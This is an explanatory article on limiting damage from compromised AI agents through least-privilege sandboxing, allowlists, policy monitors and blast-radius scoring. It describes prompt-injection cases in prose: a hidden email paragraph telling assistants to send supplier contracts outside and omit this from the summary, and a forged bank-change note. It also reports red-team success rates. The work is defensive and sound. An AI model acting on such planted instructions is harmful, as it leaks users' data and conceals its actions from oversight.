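# Least-privilege sandboxing and retrieval allowlisting: limiting the damage a compromised AI agent can do

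## How an agent is compromised and where the two controls act

An AI agent is a language model that acts through tools. Unlike a plain chatbot, which only writes replies, an agent can search a mailbox, open files, browse the web or run commands on a computer. To use a tool, the model produces a tool call, which is a structured request to run one tool with given arguments. Ordinary software around the model then runs the tool and returns the result. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) describes this arrangement as a model calling tools in a loop for a user who has stated the task in everyday language.

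Much of the text that passes through this loop comes from strangers. Anyone who can send the user an email, edit a web page or contribute to a shared document can try to steer an agent that reads it. In this technique, called indirect prompt injection, an attacker places instructions in content the agent will read, and the model follows them as if they came from the user. An agent compromised this way acts for the attacker with the user's permissions.

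Least-privilege sandboxing gives the agent only the permissions its task requires and enforces them from outside the model. Retrieval allowlisting lets the agent receive text only from listed sources. Both controls limit the damage from an attack even if the model doesn't recognize it.

### One attack, step by step

Suppose a purchasing manager asks an agent to summarize the week's emails from suppliers. The agent has tools to search the mailbox, read messages, send messages and open files on a shared drive. It needs only the first two for the summary. It has the others because the manager sometimes wants it to answer suppliers and attach price lists.

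The model's first tool call searches for messages from the past week that mention orders or prices. The software runs the search, and further calls add the text of nine messages to the model's context, the text from which the model produces its next output. This is called retrieval, and with a large document collection the software often retrieves by similarity instead. According to *SoK*, a survey of attacks on agents (Dehghantanha, 2026), the software converts the query into a numerical form, finds the stored passages closest to it and appends them to the context. Either way, text by outside authors ends up in the context alongside the manager's request.

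Eight of the messages concern deliveries and prices. The ninth comes from an address the company has never dealt with. It looks like a sales offer, but a paragraph below the offer, in white type on a white background, instructs AI assistants to send the current supplier contracts to an outside address "for verification" and to leave this step out of the summary. The model's next tool call opens the contracts folder, and another sends a message with the contracts attached. The software runs both calls because the manager's account has permission for both, and the manager receives a tidy summary of the week's offers.

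The request and the attack reached the model as text in one context, and the model acted on both without any password leaking or program malfunctioning.

The clean summary at the end is realistic. Dziemian, Lin and colleagues (2026) ran a public attack competition with 41 scenarios, described in *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* In most scenarios, an attack counted only if the agent carried out the harmful action and its final answer gave no sign of it. In one, a user asks for urgent emails, and a fake marketing message gets the agent to mark a notice about a critical deadline as read and leave it out of the summary. Most agent products show a log of tool calls, but Dziemian and colleagues consider such logs too long and complex for people to inspect in practice.

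A model that ignored every instruction in the material it reads would resist this attack, but it would be much less useful, since an agent learns how to use a tool from the tool's documentation, which consists of instructions somebody else wrote. Christodorescu and colleagues describe an agent that is asked to summarize a software issue, finds that it depends on another issue, and sensibly summarizes both. They distinguish this from an attack by where the new instruction came from and how far it changes the task. Current agents lack good ways to determine where an instruction came from.

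### The confused deputy and least privilege

Programs misused borrowed authority long before language models existed. Hardy (1988), in *The Confused Deputy*, tells a "nearly true story" from Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Tymshare's compiler, a program that translates source code, let users name a file to receive debugging output. The compiler also had permission to write in its own directory, where it recorded statistics and where the company kept its billing records. One user named the billing file as the destination for debugging output. The operating system allowed the write because the compiler had permission to write in that directory, and the billing records were lost.

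The compiler had authority from both the user who ran it and the company that installed it, but it could not specify which authority it was using when it opened a file. This is the confused deputy problem, in which a program misuses authority that it holds on someone else's behalf. Hardy considered the obvious repairs and found problems with each. A check for the name of the billing file would miss other sensitive files, and a ban on writing to the whole directory would block people with a legitimate reason to write there. The rules for opening a file eventually needed fourteen logical operators. Hardy's solution was the capability, which Saltzer and Schroeder define as an unforgeable ticket that proves its holder's right to a particular object. If the compiler had needed a ticket from the user to write debugging output, it could not have written that output to the billing file, because the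 user had no ticket for that file.

The purchasing manager's agent is the same kind of deputy. The sender of the ninth email could not open the contracts folder, but the agent could, and the email supplied the request. The agent is in one respect more vulnerable than the compiler, because it has no separate slot for commands, while the compiler at least received the file name in a slot meant for file names.

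The usual remedy is the principle of least privilege, which goes back to Saltzer and Schroeder's *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975). It holds that programs and users should run with "the least set of privileges necessary to complete the job". Saltzer and Schroeder valued it mainly because it limits the damage from an accident or error, even one nobody foresaw. In the supplier summary example, the agent can still search and read mail, but it can no longer send mail or use the shared drive. The hidden paragraph still reaches the model, which may issue the same tool calls, but those calls fail.

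Least privilege is hard to apply to an agent because its purpose isn't known until the user states it. A phone app has a fixed purpose, so its developer can list the permissions it needs when the user installs it. Christodorescu and colleagues give the example of a user asking an agent to comment on a particular software issue. The agent needs to open that issue and write in its comment box, and should have no other access to the site. If the user then asks for a summary of the same issue, the agent needs different permissions, and by then its context may already contain an attacker's text.

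Some tasks also need the same permission that an attacker wants. If the manager had asked the agent to answer the suppliers, it would have needed permission to send mail. The deadline attack in the competition used an action close to the agent's ordinary work, since sorting email includes marking it as read. Least privilege reduces the number of harmful actions a compromised agent can take, but most useful tasks still leave at least one available.

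### Where each control acts

The path from the ninth email to the stolen contracts runs through the model, and the controls sit on either side of it.

The retrieval allowlist acts before the text reaches the model. If the software admits only messages from the company's registered suppliers, it drops the ninth email and the model never processes the hidden paragraph. The control fails when the attacker writes from inside an approved source, such as a real supplier's hijacked mailbox. *How we contain Claude across products*, a May 2026 account by Anthropic, which makes the Claude models, warns that "an audited connector isn't the same as audited data". A connector is software that links an agent to an outside service. A connector for the code-hosting site GitHub, for example, can pass every malware check and still load a poisoned file into the context.

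The other controls act after the model has produced a tool call. The first is the policy monitor, ordinary code that compares the call with fixed rules before anything runs. A rule that summary tasks may not send mail stops the theft at this point. Dehghantanha recommends treating the model as an untrusted code generator whose output the operator has to validate before execution. If the monitor allows the call, it runs in the sandbox, an environment that limits which files, processes and network addresses the agent's tools can reach. If the contracts folder is outside the sandbox, a call that the monitor wrongly allows still cannot open the files in it.

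A sandbox usually includes an egress allowlist, which lists the only network destinations it may send traffic to. Restricting where data can go is close to what Saltzer and Schroeder called confinement, which means letting a borrowed program use data while making sure it cannot release the data. A retrieval allowlist instead restricts whose words can influence the model. People often confuse the two, partly because both may be lists of web domains.

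A site that is safe to send data to may be unsafe to read from, and vice versa. For example, a company wiki that any employee can edit may be a harmless place to send data but a risky one to read from. A programming agent may need to download software packages from a public site without ever needing to read the discussion pages there. A single web request can carry stolen data out in the address it asks for and bring instructions in through the page that comes back. If an operator uses only an egress allowlist, a stranger's email can still induce the agent to delete files, because deletion sends no data out. With only a retrieval allowlist, one poisoned document from an approved source can induce the agent to send data to any address on the internet.

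The supplier attack shows another weakness of egress allowlists. The contracts left by email through the company's own mail server, which any agent that sends mail must be able to reach. The allowlist would have blocked an upload to the attacker's website but let the email through. Anthropic now regards an egress allowlist as a "capability grant" because approving a destination exposes every function available there to misuse. Stopping the email requires a rule about recipients, which belongs in the policy monitor.

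### Why designers assume that some injections will succeed

These controls take effort and remove some of the agent's abilities. A simpler alternative might be to ask the user before each risky step. Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent, originally worked this way, and Anthropic found that users approved roughly 93% of permission prompts. Most of those requests were presumably harmless, so the approval rate alone does not prove carelessness. But users paid less attention to each prompt as they saw more of them, and one inattentive approval is enough for an attack to succeed.

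The other candidate is a model that does not follow injected instructions, and models have improved quickly at this. On a benchmark from Gray Swan, a company that tests AI systems by attacking them, a single strong attack succeeded 4.7% of the time against Claude Opus 4.5, and at least one of 100 attempts succeeded 63% of the time, according to The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*. For the later Claude Opus 4.7, Anthropic reported success rates of about 0.1% for a single attempt and 5 to 6% after 100 adaptive attempts, in which the attacker changes the attack in response to failures.

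Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1, published in September, gives newer figures. They come from a different Gray Swan test, which used 1,804 attacks that had worked across several models, so they are not exactly comparable with the older figures.

| Model | One attempt | After 15 attempts |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5.1 | 0.1% | 1.0% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 0.4% | 4.8% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 0.6% | 6.5% |
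| Gemini 3.7 Flash, the best model from another developer | not stated | 9.2% |
| Most other developers' models | not stated | 24% to 53% |

Anthropic's *Introducing Claude Fable 5.2 and Claude Mythos 5.2* (2026) announced Fable 5.1's successor on 9 November. *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense* (Cross, 2026) relays OpenAI's own October figures for GPT-6 Sol, which are 97.13% robustness against indirect injection and 99.99% against direct injection. The lower figure matters more for agents because they spend their time reading other people's text.

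Such progress may well reduce the need for outside controls. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reported that no attack succeeded against Opus 5 in 129 browser scenarios when the model ran in Anthropic's own software. If a model almost never follows injected instructions, an operator may reasonably decide that a strict sandbox blocks more legitimate work than theft, especially when the agent has little access.

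Resistance to attack weakens as the attacker improves. Gray Swan built a stronger automated attacker for programming tasks, trained it on 40 scenarios and gave it 200 attempts at each of the same 40. Anthropic reported that the attacker succeeded in 57% of its attempts on Fable 5.1 and broke 38 of the 40 scenarios. Anthropic considers these conditions far more favorable than a real attacker would have, which seems right. It also traced every success to Claude Opus 4.8, an older model that answers when Fable 5.1's safety filters block a request. None of the 2,826 requests that Fable 5.1 answered itself led to a successful attack. This is encouraging about the newer model, but less reassuring for customers, because the product they use includes the fallback.

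Adding software that inspects tool results for injected instructions cut the attack success rate in the programming test from 57% to 13% of attempts, though at least one attack still succeeded in 36 of the 40 scenarios. In a separate test of 110 browser scenarios, attacks succeeded in 10 when the model had no added filters and in none when it had the same inspection software and a second filter on outgoing tool calls. Like the two controls, one filter acts on incoming text and the other on outgoing actions, but both filters are trained classifiers and can miss attacks.

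Results from outside the developers' own reports are also a reason for caution. In the competition that Dziemian and colleagues ran, 464 people made about 272,000 attempts against 13 models, most of them from late 2025. Attacks succeeded against all 13, at rates between 0.5% and 8.5% of attempts. Participants could see the conversation and knew exactly which action to aim for, so the rates are an upper bound for attacks of this type. Some of their methods worked in 21 of the 41 scenarios and on several families of models, so an attacker need not start over for each target. In a more recent benchmark, *FrontierBreach*, PromptArmor claims successful attacks on leading models from every provider, including Google's Gemini 4 Carbon, but the company sells security services and has an interest in that result.

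Low success rates are also less reassuring when an attacker can easily make many attempts. At a success rate of 0.1%, an attacker who sends one email to a thousand inboxes will compromise one agent on average. Christodorescu and colleagues argue that even if a guard correctly refuses 99% of forbidden requests, attackers will search for the remaining 1%, and that nobody can prove a language model will always refuse. The Decoder reports that OpenAI has conceded that prompt injection may never be fully solved. Dehghantanha writes that operators "must assume that any malicious instruction reaching the model may be followed".

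Better training makes a compromise less likely but doesn't limit the damage it can do. Anthropic observes that the potential damage is growing because more capable agents receive more access. By May 2026 the company routinely gave Claude enough access to take down an internal service, which it would have refused to do a year earlier. A well-trained model may be enough protection for an agent that reads public web pages and can only write a summary. But the purchasing manager's agent can open every supplier contract and send it anywhere, so even one successful attack in a thousand attempts is a serious loss.

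## Estimating the blast radius before setting limits

How strict the controls need to be depends on how much damage a successful attack could do. An agent's blast radius is everything that an attacker in control of it could read, change or send before needing a new authorization. Jarmak (2026), in *Engineering Reliable Coding Agents*, uses nearly the same definition and illustrates it with a practitioner's report from spring 2026, in which an agent deleted a production database in nine seconds and nobody could recover the backups because the same credentials reached both. The report comes from one person, but any operator can check whether the same credentials reach both its data and its backups.

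To estimate the blast radius, an operator lists what the agent holds, traces what each item can reach and scores the effects.

### Listing what the agent holds

The list covers credentials, tools, file paths and network routes. It needs to record what each credential can do, because keeping a credential secret does not prevent its misuse. *Beyond Direct Access* (2026) points out that an agent may refuse to reveal a key and still use it to carry out an outsider's request.

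An agent's credentials often belong to someone with more access than the task needs. In *Agentic Explainability at Scale* (2026), practitioners describe company agents that run with their creators' full access. One healthcare specialist explains that a colleague with no right to see patient records can get them by using an agent that an authorized person created. Agents that query databases have a similar problem when they connect through one shared account that can read far more than most of their users are allowed to see.

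For an agent on a personal computer, the list of file paths may be very long. *Local LLM Agents as Vulnerable Runtimes* (2026) examines programs such as OpenClaw and finds that every internal component, from the parser to the network client, runs with the agent's full privileges on the machine. Unless something outside the agent narrows its access, the list includes every file the agent's account can open.

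Software can draw up part of the list. *AgentFlow* (2026) analyses an agent's code and collects the prompts, models, tools, memory and other agents connected to it. Someone still has to look up what each credential allows on the server that accepts it.

### Tracing what each item reaches

An agent that cannot delete a backup may still be able to read a stored administrator token, edit an access policy or ask a more powerful service to delete the backup. Jarmak therefore wants the inventory to cover every such delegation.

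In *PRISM*, Luo, Shen and colleagues (2026) automate the tracing with a graph of tools. They draw an arrow from one tool to another if the first returns the type of data that the second requires. They also add an arrow wherever text from one tool's output reappears in a later tool's input during test runs. Following the arrows from the tool where an attack enters shows which tools the attacker could reach. In 200 random checks, the graph found 93.8% of the tools that were actually reachable and included 0.7 unreachable tools on average. In all seven cases it missed, the model had passed on a credential in ordinary language.

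A list of permissions also misses routes that run through messages between agents. *Towards Security-Auditable LLM Agents* (2026) follows a tampered message that changes one agent's role and goal and then spreads to another agent. The opposite mistake is to count every theoretical connection as real. *A Theory of Least Autonomy in AI* (2026) treats a link between two permissions as an established channel only if a feasible workflow connects them.

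Some effects appear only when permitted steps combine. *Data Agents Under Attack* (Wang, Wang and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a tax database that answers questions about totals. An attacker asks for the total over all regions, then for the total over all regions except North. If only one taxpayer lives in North, the difference is that person's exact tax, although both queries were allowed. A trace should therefore include combinations of permissions, especially pairs where one reads confidential data and the other sends data out.

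### Scoring severity and reversibility

Muruaga (2026), in *Bounded Agents*, scores each resource r between 0 and 1:

blast(r) = 0.4 × scope + 0.4 × irreversibility + 0.2 × sensitivity

Scope is how many people or systems an action would affect, irreversibility is how hard the effect would be to undo, and sensitivity is how confidential the data is. Operators can change the weights. Muruaga's illustrative scores are 0.14 for a calendar entry, 0.40 for a shared team document, 0.72 for a customer's personal record, 0.78 for sending external email and 0.88 for a production database. Email scores high mainly because nobody can recall a sent message.

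A weighted sum can hide one extreme value. For example, a resource with a sensitivity of 1.0 and 0.1 on the other two factors scores only 0.28. In *SoK: Trust-Authorization Mismatch in LLM Agent Interactions*, Shi, Du and colleagues instead take the highest of three similar factors, which would give the same resource 1.0. Taking the maximum is safer for deciding which actions need approval, but less useful for ranking resources because it puts so many near the top.

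Scores attached to tools also don't reflect what a file contains. The scale in *Treating the Model as an Untrusted Component* (Aljumaily, Alseelawi and Alshabandar, 2026) runs from 3 for writing a file to 10 for sending confidential data out. A false safety report therefore scores 3, the same as any other file. An operator whose staff act on such reports should score them higher.

### Expressing the result

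The simplest summary of the blast radius is everything an attacker can reach. Luo and colleagues measure it as the percentage of high-risk tools that an attacker can reach from the most damaging entry point. Their method of removing unneeded tools reduced this share from 100% to 15.9% on three benchmarks, while task success fell only from 79.4% to 78.2%. Counting permissions alone would have been misleading. When they left out the step that plans for an attacker who chooses the most damaging entry point, the share rose to 27.3% with almost no change in task success.

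This percentage is easy to compute and compare between two configurations, but it gives a tool that posts a comment the same weight as one that transfers money. It also leaves out read-only tools on two of the three benchmarks, though Jarmak warns that a read-only agent can still disclose whatever it reads.

Wang and colleagues instead grade how far an attack spreads, on a scale from BR0 to BR4. They ran 150 hijacking attacks against each of four open-source data agents, which answer questions by querying databases and running code. The table gives the results for two of the agents.

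| Level | How far the effect spreads | DataInterpreter | DB-GPT |
|---|---|---|---|
| BR0 | No unauthorized effect | 76.0% | 59.3% |
| BR1 | One response | 6.7% | 10.7% |
| BR2 | The rest of the session | 8.0% | 18.7% |
| BR3 | The agent's container or sandbox | 0.0% | 11.3% |
| BR4 | The host computer, the network or files outside the workspace | 9.3% | 0.0% |

Attacks succeeded less often against DataInterpreter than against DB-GPT, but DataInterpreter had the largest share of attacks at BR4. Many attacks on DataInterpreter failed only because it often could not connect to the database. DB-GPT runs code in a container, and no attack escaped it. The other two agents reached BR4 in 2.7% and 4.7% of attacks. Some BR4 attacks installed scheduled jobs that kept running the attacker's commands.

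The levels work well for comparing sandboxes, but they measure how far an attack reaches rather than how much damage it does. A single response that lists every customer's address would presumably count as BR1, while a harmless file written outside the workspace would count as BR4. An operator also has to run attacks to get the distribution, so before deployment they can only use the scale to guess the worst level.

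### A formal maximum for chains of agents

Muruaga's definition covers systems in which one agent hands work to others. The user, p₀, authorizes a main agent, p₁, which may pass part of the task to a sub-agent, p₂, and so on. A gateway outside the models keeps account of what each agent may do. The maximal blast radius of the agent at position i is:

BRmax(pᵢ) = R(S(pᵢ)) ∩ { r : blast(r) ≤ βmax(pᵢ) − βconsumed(pᵢ) }

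S(pᵢ) is the agent's scope, which sets out its permitted resources, actions and classes of data, along with forbidden combinations of actions. R(S(pᵢ)) is the set of resources in that scope. The part in braces is the set of resources whose score fits within the agent's remaining budget, which is the ceiling βmax minus βconsumed, the amount the chain has already used. The symbol ∩ means the intersection of the two sets, so the agent can reach a resource only if it has permission for it and the resource's score fits within the remaining budget.

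Suppose a main agent has permission for all five resources that Muruaga scored. Its budget ceiling is 1.0, and it has already used 0.2 (both figures are invented). With 0.8 left, it can reach all of them except the production database. If it then starts a sub-agent, Muruaga by default sets the new ceiling at 70% of the parent's, here 0.7, and the sub-agent inherits the 0.2 already used. The sub-agent has 0.5 left and can reach only the team document and the calendar entry, even if it still has permission for the other three.

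Muruaga proves that a sub-agent can never reach anything its parent cannot: BRmax(pᵢ) ⊆ BRmax(pᵢ₋₁) at every step. The gateway intersects the parent's scope with the sub-agent's role, so the sub-agent's scope contains nothing outside the parent's. The sub-agent's ceiling is no higher than the parent's and its spending starts at no less than the parent's, so its remaining budget is no larger. Any resource that fits the sub-agent's budget therefore also fits the parent's. BRmax is the set of resources that are both in scope and within budget, so the sub-agent's BRmax is contained in the parent's.

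The proof requires every agent in the chain to use the same scores, but the scores don't have to be right. If someone gives the production database a score of 0.05, the theorem still holds, but a score that low would let nearly every sub-agent with permission for the database touch it. Muruaga writes that the specific values affect only how tight the bound is. This is mathematically true, but an operator relying on the bound needs it to be tight around the resources that matter. In the incident Jarmak describes, for example, anyone who assumed that backups existed would have rated the loss of the database as reversible, and only tracing the credential would have corrected this.

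Every action must also go through the gateway. If a sub-agent finds a password in a file and connects directly to a server, the gateway deducts nothing from its budget. The theorem applies to one chain at a time, so two sub-agents with 0.5 left each may do more harm together than either could alone, unless the gateway counts both against a shared budget. The blast radius also need not shrink under the theorem, since a parent may pass on everything it has.

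Muruaga tested the whole system by inserting the attacker's tool call directly into 609 combinations of task and attack, as if the model had obeyed. The system reduced the success rate of data theft from between 75% and 100%, depending on the type of task and attack, to zero. Destructive actions fell from 38.6% to 4.0%. The system also lowered the task completion rate by 8.6 percentage points when a simulated human could approve risky steps, and by 13.9 points otherwise.

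Most of the protection against theft came from a separate rule that forbids combinations such as reading confidential data and then sending a message outside. On another benchmark, that rule stopped all 544 attempted data thefts, but removing one forbidden pair from the list let 39.9% of them succeed. On the same benchmark, 60.4% of attacks that needed only one harmful action still worked because the agent had permission for that action.

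### From blast radius to expected harm

The blast radius describes what could happen if an attack succeeds. To compare controls, an operator also needs a rough idea of how often attacks will succeed. A simple model multiplies four factors:

expected harm = attacker-controlled items read × chance the model obeys × chance the action is permitted × severity

A retrieval allowlist lowers the number of attacker-controlled items that reach the agent. Better training and filters that detect injections lower the chance that the model follows them. Least privilege, enforced by a policy monitor and a sandbox, lowers the chance that the resulting action is permitted. It can also lower severity, for example by giving the agent one customer's record instead of the whole database. Backups also lower severity if the agent cannot reach them, because they make a deletion reversible.

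Aljumaily and colleagues measured the two middle factors separately on two small open models. The models ran behind a monitor that admits only calls authorized by the user's request. They proposed the attacker's call in 64% and 84% of attacks, and the monitor let it through in 1.3% and 7.7% of all attacks. This works out to the monitor permitting about 2% and 9% of the proposed calls. The best current models obey injected instructions far less often than these two, but the protection the monitor adds does not depend on how often a model obeys.

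When estimating the chance that an action is permitted, the operator should consider the action a sensible attacker would choose. An attacker who knows that an agent can send email but not delete files will ask it to send email. Averaging severity can similarly obscure a rare but ruinous effect, so the operator should estimate the worst case separately, and can assume for that estimate that the model always obeys the attacker.

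### Repeated attempts

The model gives an average, but an operator may also want to know the chance of at least one success. If each attempt succeeds independently with probability p, that chance is 1 − (1 − p)^k after k attempts. With p = 2%, it is 18% after 10 attempts and 87% after 100.

Real attack attempts are often not independent. *BrowseSafe++* (2026) tested agents on 1,024 browser tasks, first with a fixed attack and then with up to 64 attempts that adapted to the agent's responses.

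| Model | First attempt | Formula for 64 attempts | Measured, up to 64 attempts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Sonnet 5 | 2.05% | 73% | 30.66% |
| GPT-5.5 | 0.49% | 27% | 65.23% |

The formula overestimates the risk for Sonnet 5 and underestimates it for GPT-5.5. It overestimates when a low average success rate comes from a few easy scenarios and many where attacks almost never succeed, because repeating an attack on a resistant scenario gains little. It underestimates when attackers learn from failures, because the chance of success, p, then rises with each attempt. Both effects probably occur in most tests, and their balance differs between models.

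*LLMail-Inject* (2025), a public competition in attacking an email agent, also shows how much the odds of a successful attack vary. Against one type of defence, the teams that succeeded needed 89 attempts on average before their first success, with a standard deviation of 426. If every attempt had the same chance of success, the standard deviation would be about as large as the average. Evidently some teams succeeded quickly, while others needed thousands of attempts.

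Where a measured curve exists, it is therefore better than the formula. *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms* (2026) reports the share of scenarios that withstand the first k adaptive attempts, which gives the needed figure without assuming independence. The formula is still reasonable for a quick estimate when unrelated attackers each try once. The expected number of successes is k × p even if the attempts aren't independent, provided p is the true average success probability over those attempts.

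### A worked inventory

In this invented example, an online shop's agent answers customers' emails about their orders and issues small refunds. The numbers are also invented, and the scores use Muruaga's weights. The figures in brackets are scope, irreversibility and sensitivity.

| Permission | What it reaches | Score before | After the cuts | Score after |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ticket inbox | Every ticket, open or closed | 0.64 (0.5, 0.8, 0.6) | The current ticket | 0.48 (0.1, 0.8, 0.6) |
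| Customer database, shared account | Reading and changing 200,000 records | 0.86 (0.9, 0.8, 0.9) | Reading the record of the ticket's customer | 0.54 (0.1, 0.8, 0.9) |
| Refund tool | Any amount on any order | 0.48 (0.5, 0.6, 0.2) | Up to $50 on the ticket's order | 0.32 (0.1, 0.6, 0.2) |
| Email | Any address | 0.78 (0.7, 1.0, 0.5) | Replies to the ticket's sender | 0.54 (0.1, 1.0, 0.5) |
| Shared drive | A file with an administrator key to the database and its backups | 0.92 (0.9, 1.0, 0.8) | Removed | – |
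| Web requests | Any internet address | 0.78 (0.7, 1.0, 0.5) | Removed | – |
| Messages to the billing agent | Suppliers' bank details | 0.68 (0.6, 0.8, 0.6) | Removed | – |

The shared drive has the highest score only because of the tracing. Without the key, it would score 0.40, like Muruaga's shared team document. The billing agent also looks harmless if no one checks what it can do on request.

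To find out which permissions the agent needs, the shop can remove them one at a time in a test environment and check whether the agent still does its work. Luo and colleagues did this for an agent that finds failed software releases in log files and reports them. The agent had used a command-line tool in 31% of its runs, so permissions based on past use would have included it. Without that tool, the agent read copies of the logs and succeeded about as often. When they removed the tool for reading files, success fell from 93% to 5%.

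The cuts lower the highest score from 0.92 to 0.54. Before them, an attacker could reach six permissions that change something or send data out. Now only refunds and replies remain. The narrower permissions work only if ordinary software decides which customer a ticket belongs to, because a hidden instruction can make the model choose a different customer.

Suppose the agent reads 100 malicious items a month, 80 in emails and 20 on web pages, and the model follows the instructions in 1% of them. Before the cuts, the agent's permissions allow 90% of the actions attackers choose, and we use the worst severity score, 0.92. The expected harm is 100 × 0.01 × 0.9 × 0.92, or about 0.83 a month. Removing web access leaves 80 items. If the remaining permissions allow 20% of the chosen actions and the worst score is 0.54, expected harm falls to about 0.09 a month, almost a tenfold reduction. A retrieval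 allowlist could do little about the remaining 80 items, because a support agent has to read email from strangers.

Much of that reduction depends on attackers not knowing what the agent may do. If they ask only for permitted actions, the permitted share of their requests stays at 100% after the cuts, and expected harm falls only from 0.92 to 0.43. Even that smaller drop understates the benefit, because a scale that stops at 1 compresses large differences. The database score drops from 0.86 to 0.54, while the number of records that one successful attack can expose drops from 200,000 to one. The shop should use the scores to decide which permissions to examine first, and count records or money when deciding whether a restriction is worth the work it would block.

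## Setting tool permissions for each task

The online shop could restrict its support agent's permissions once, because every ticket needs the same few actions. A general office assistant needs different permissions for each request. In *Taming Various Privilege Escalation in LLM-Based Agent Systems*, Ji, Wu and colleagues (2026) define the ideal permissions for a request as the smallest set of actions that fulfills it, including the arguments of each tool call. They count any action outside that set as a privilege escalation. They concede that nobody usually knows this set beforehand. A permission system can therefore only approximate it, and a closer approximation requires more information about the request.

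### One invoice, four restrictions

Suppose a purchasing manager tells an AI agent, "Send this invoice to the accounts department," and attaches a supplier's PDF in which an attacker has hidden instructions. The agent opens the PDF to get the amount for a covering note. The agent has tools for files, contacts, email, web requests and shell commands, all of which run with the manager's permissions.

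The coarsest restriction removes whole tools. *Capability Minimization as a Safety Primitive* (2026) treats the tools a model can see as standing authority, which the model holds even at steps that don't need it. The invoice task needs only files, contacts and email, so removing the web and shell tools stops the attacker from running programs or uploading anything to a website. But the hidden instructions can still make the agent email the supplier contracts to an outsider. They can also make it delete the invoices folder or replace the accounts department's address in the contacts list, because the file and contacts tools can write as well as read.

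Goel (2026), in *Security Risks in Tool-Enabled AI Agents*, ran a small test of removing tools from an agent. The agent ran on GPT-5.1 and had five tools, including a shell. Goel ran it ten times in each of four scenarios, first without and then with a countermeasure. In one scenario the agent only had to read and write files, but in 40% of runs it did something beyond the task, such as using the shell. An allowlist of tools reduced this to zero, while task success fell from 70% to 60%. In two other scenarios the agent leaked secrets in every run without a countermeasure, and in none when Goel removed the secrets from its environment or checked its scripts against a policy.

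The exception was the scenario with injected instructions, where unsafe behavior fell only from 90% to 50% of runs, a relative reduction of 44%. The countermeasure in that scenario was a content filter, and the agent kept all its tools, so the result is not evidence about permission limits. All these numbers are rough, because the loss in task success amounts to a single run and zero unsafe runs out of ten is compatible with a true rate of up to about 26%.

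The next restriction makes the file and contact tools read-only. The agent can still open files and look up contacts, but it can't delete the invoices or change an address. It still has to send email to do its task, and an attacker who can make it read files and send email can steal the contracts. The manager could limit the agent to writing drafts and send them personally. That helps if the manager reads the drafts, which is doubtful for someone who approves dozens a day.

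A finer restriction checks a call's arguments as well as the tool. The company's administrator might allow email only to company addresses and attachments only from the invoices folder. The agent then can't email the contracts outside the company. It could still send other suppliers' invoices to a colleague who has no right to see them, or write to the whole staff in the manager's name and ask them to log in at the attacker's website. A standing rule has to allow everything the manager might ask for, so it can't be much tighter than this.

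A task-bound permission can be tighter because it comes from the request. Before the agent opens the invoice, the policy monitor receives a rule that permits one message to the accounts department's address in the company directory, with only the invoice attached. The hidden instructions cannot influence the rule because no model has read them yet. If the agent later tries to send the contracts, the call fails because it matches no rule.

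The agent could still misuse the covering note. It could write that the supplier has changed banks and wants payment to a new account, and the message would still have the correct sender, recipients and attachment. This may be the most expensive attack for a department that pays invoices. A stricter rule could set the wording of the note and leave a blank only for the amount. Even then, an attacker who can edit the invoice can put a false account number on it. No permission on sending email prevents that, so the accounts department has to check bank details against its own records.

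Many companies already use just-in-time access, which looks similar. A person or program asks for a credential and gets it for a limited time. *Empirical Evaluation of Task-Based Permission Scoping Architecture for AI Agents* (2026) points out that such systems do not derive the permissions from the content of the task. If the agent gets access to the manager's whole mailbox for ten minutes, an attacker who compromises the agent can use the whole mailbox during that time.

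### How Progent turns a request into rules

Shi, He and colleagues (2025) built a policy monitor called Progent that works with task-bound rules. In simplified notation, its rule for the invoice might look like this:

```
allow send_email
  when to = "accounts@example.com"
  and attachments = ["invoice-4471.pdf"]
```

Each rule names a tool, allows or forbids it, and sets conditions on its arguments, which can be exact values, patterns or numeric limits. For every tool call, Progent checks the forbid rules first and then the allow rules, and it blocks any call that matches neither. By default, the agent gets an error message when a call is blocked and can continue the legitimate part of the task. An operator can instead have Progent stop the agent or ask the user.

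A language model writes the first policy from the user's request and the list of tools, before it sees any outside text. This works well for the invoice, but for some requests the agent learns what steps are needed only as it works. In an example from Shi and colleagues, a user asks the agent to carry out the to-do list in an email from Alice. The first policy permits only a search for that email. The list includes posting a summary of recent emails to the user's workplace chat, so the agent now needs permission to read mail and post messages. One of the recent emails then contains a hidden instruction to forward the inbox to a stranger. Both the to-do list and the hidden instruction arrive in text that a tool returned, and following either one requires a wider policy.

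Progent therefore treats wider and narrower policies differently. After each tool call, a model decides whether the policy might need to change, without seeing what the tool returned. If so, the model reads the result and proposes a new policy, P′. An SMT solver, which is a program that can prove whether a logical condition holds for all possible values, compares P′ with the current policy P. Let A(P) be the set of all tool calls that P allows. If A(P′) ⊆ A(P), the new policy allows nothing that the old one didn't, and it takes effect at once. If not, it needs approval. Between two approvals, the set of allowed calls can only stay the same or shrink:

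A(P₀) ⊇ A(P₁) ⊇ A(P₂) ⊇ …

An injection may fool the model that writes the updates, but it can't add a permission without approval.

Shi and colleagues tested Progent with GPT-4o on AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated office, banking, travel and chat tasks. The attack success rate fell from 39.9% to 1.0%, and the agent completed about as many legitimate tasks as before. In these runs, the system automatically approved every wider policy to imitate a careless user. The first policy without updates reduced the attack success rate to 2.5%. No attack succeeded when a security-conscious person reviewed the rules.

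*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) argues that the update step still relies on a model to filter out malicious instructions, so a poisoned tool result may loosen the policy. The approval step solves this only if the approver judges well. People who see constant permission prompts often judge poorly, but only 6% of Progent's updates widened the policy, so a person could plausibly read each of those.

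The AgentDojo results are less informative about current models. *RATION* (Du, Chaudhari and colleagues, 2026) found that only 0.2% of a standard set of AgentDojo attacks succeeded against GPT-5.4 without any outside control. Progent is useful for such a model only if it stops attacks that the model does not resist.

### Who writes the policy

*The 2026 Singapore Consensus on Global AI Safety Research Priorities* (2026) divides responsibility for least privilege between an agent's developers and its deployers. Developers should tie permissions to the current task and define which actions always fall outside it. Deployers should adapt the limits to their own setting and decide which further actions need new authorization.

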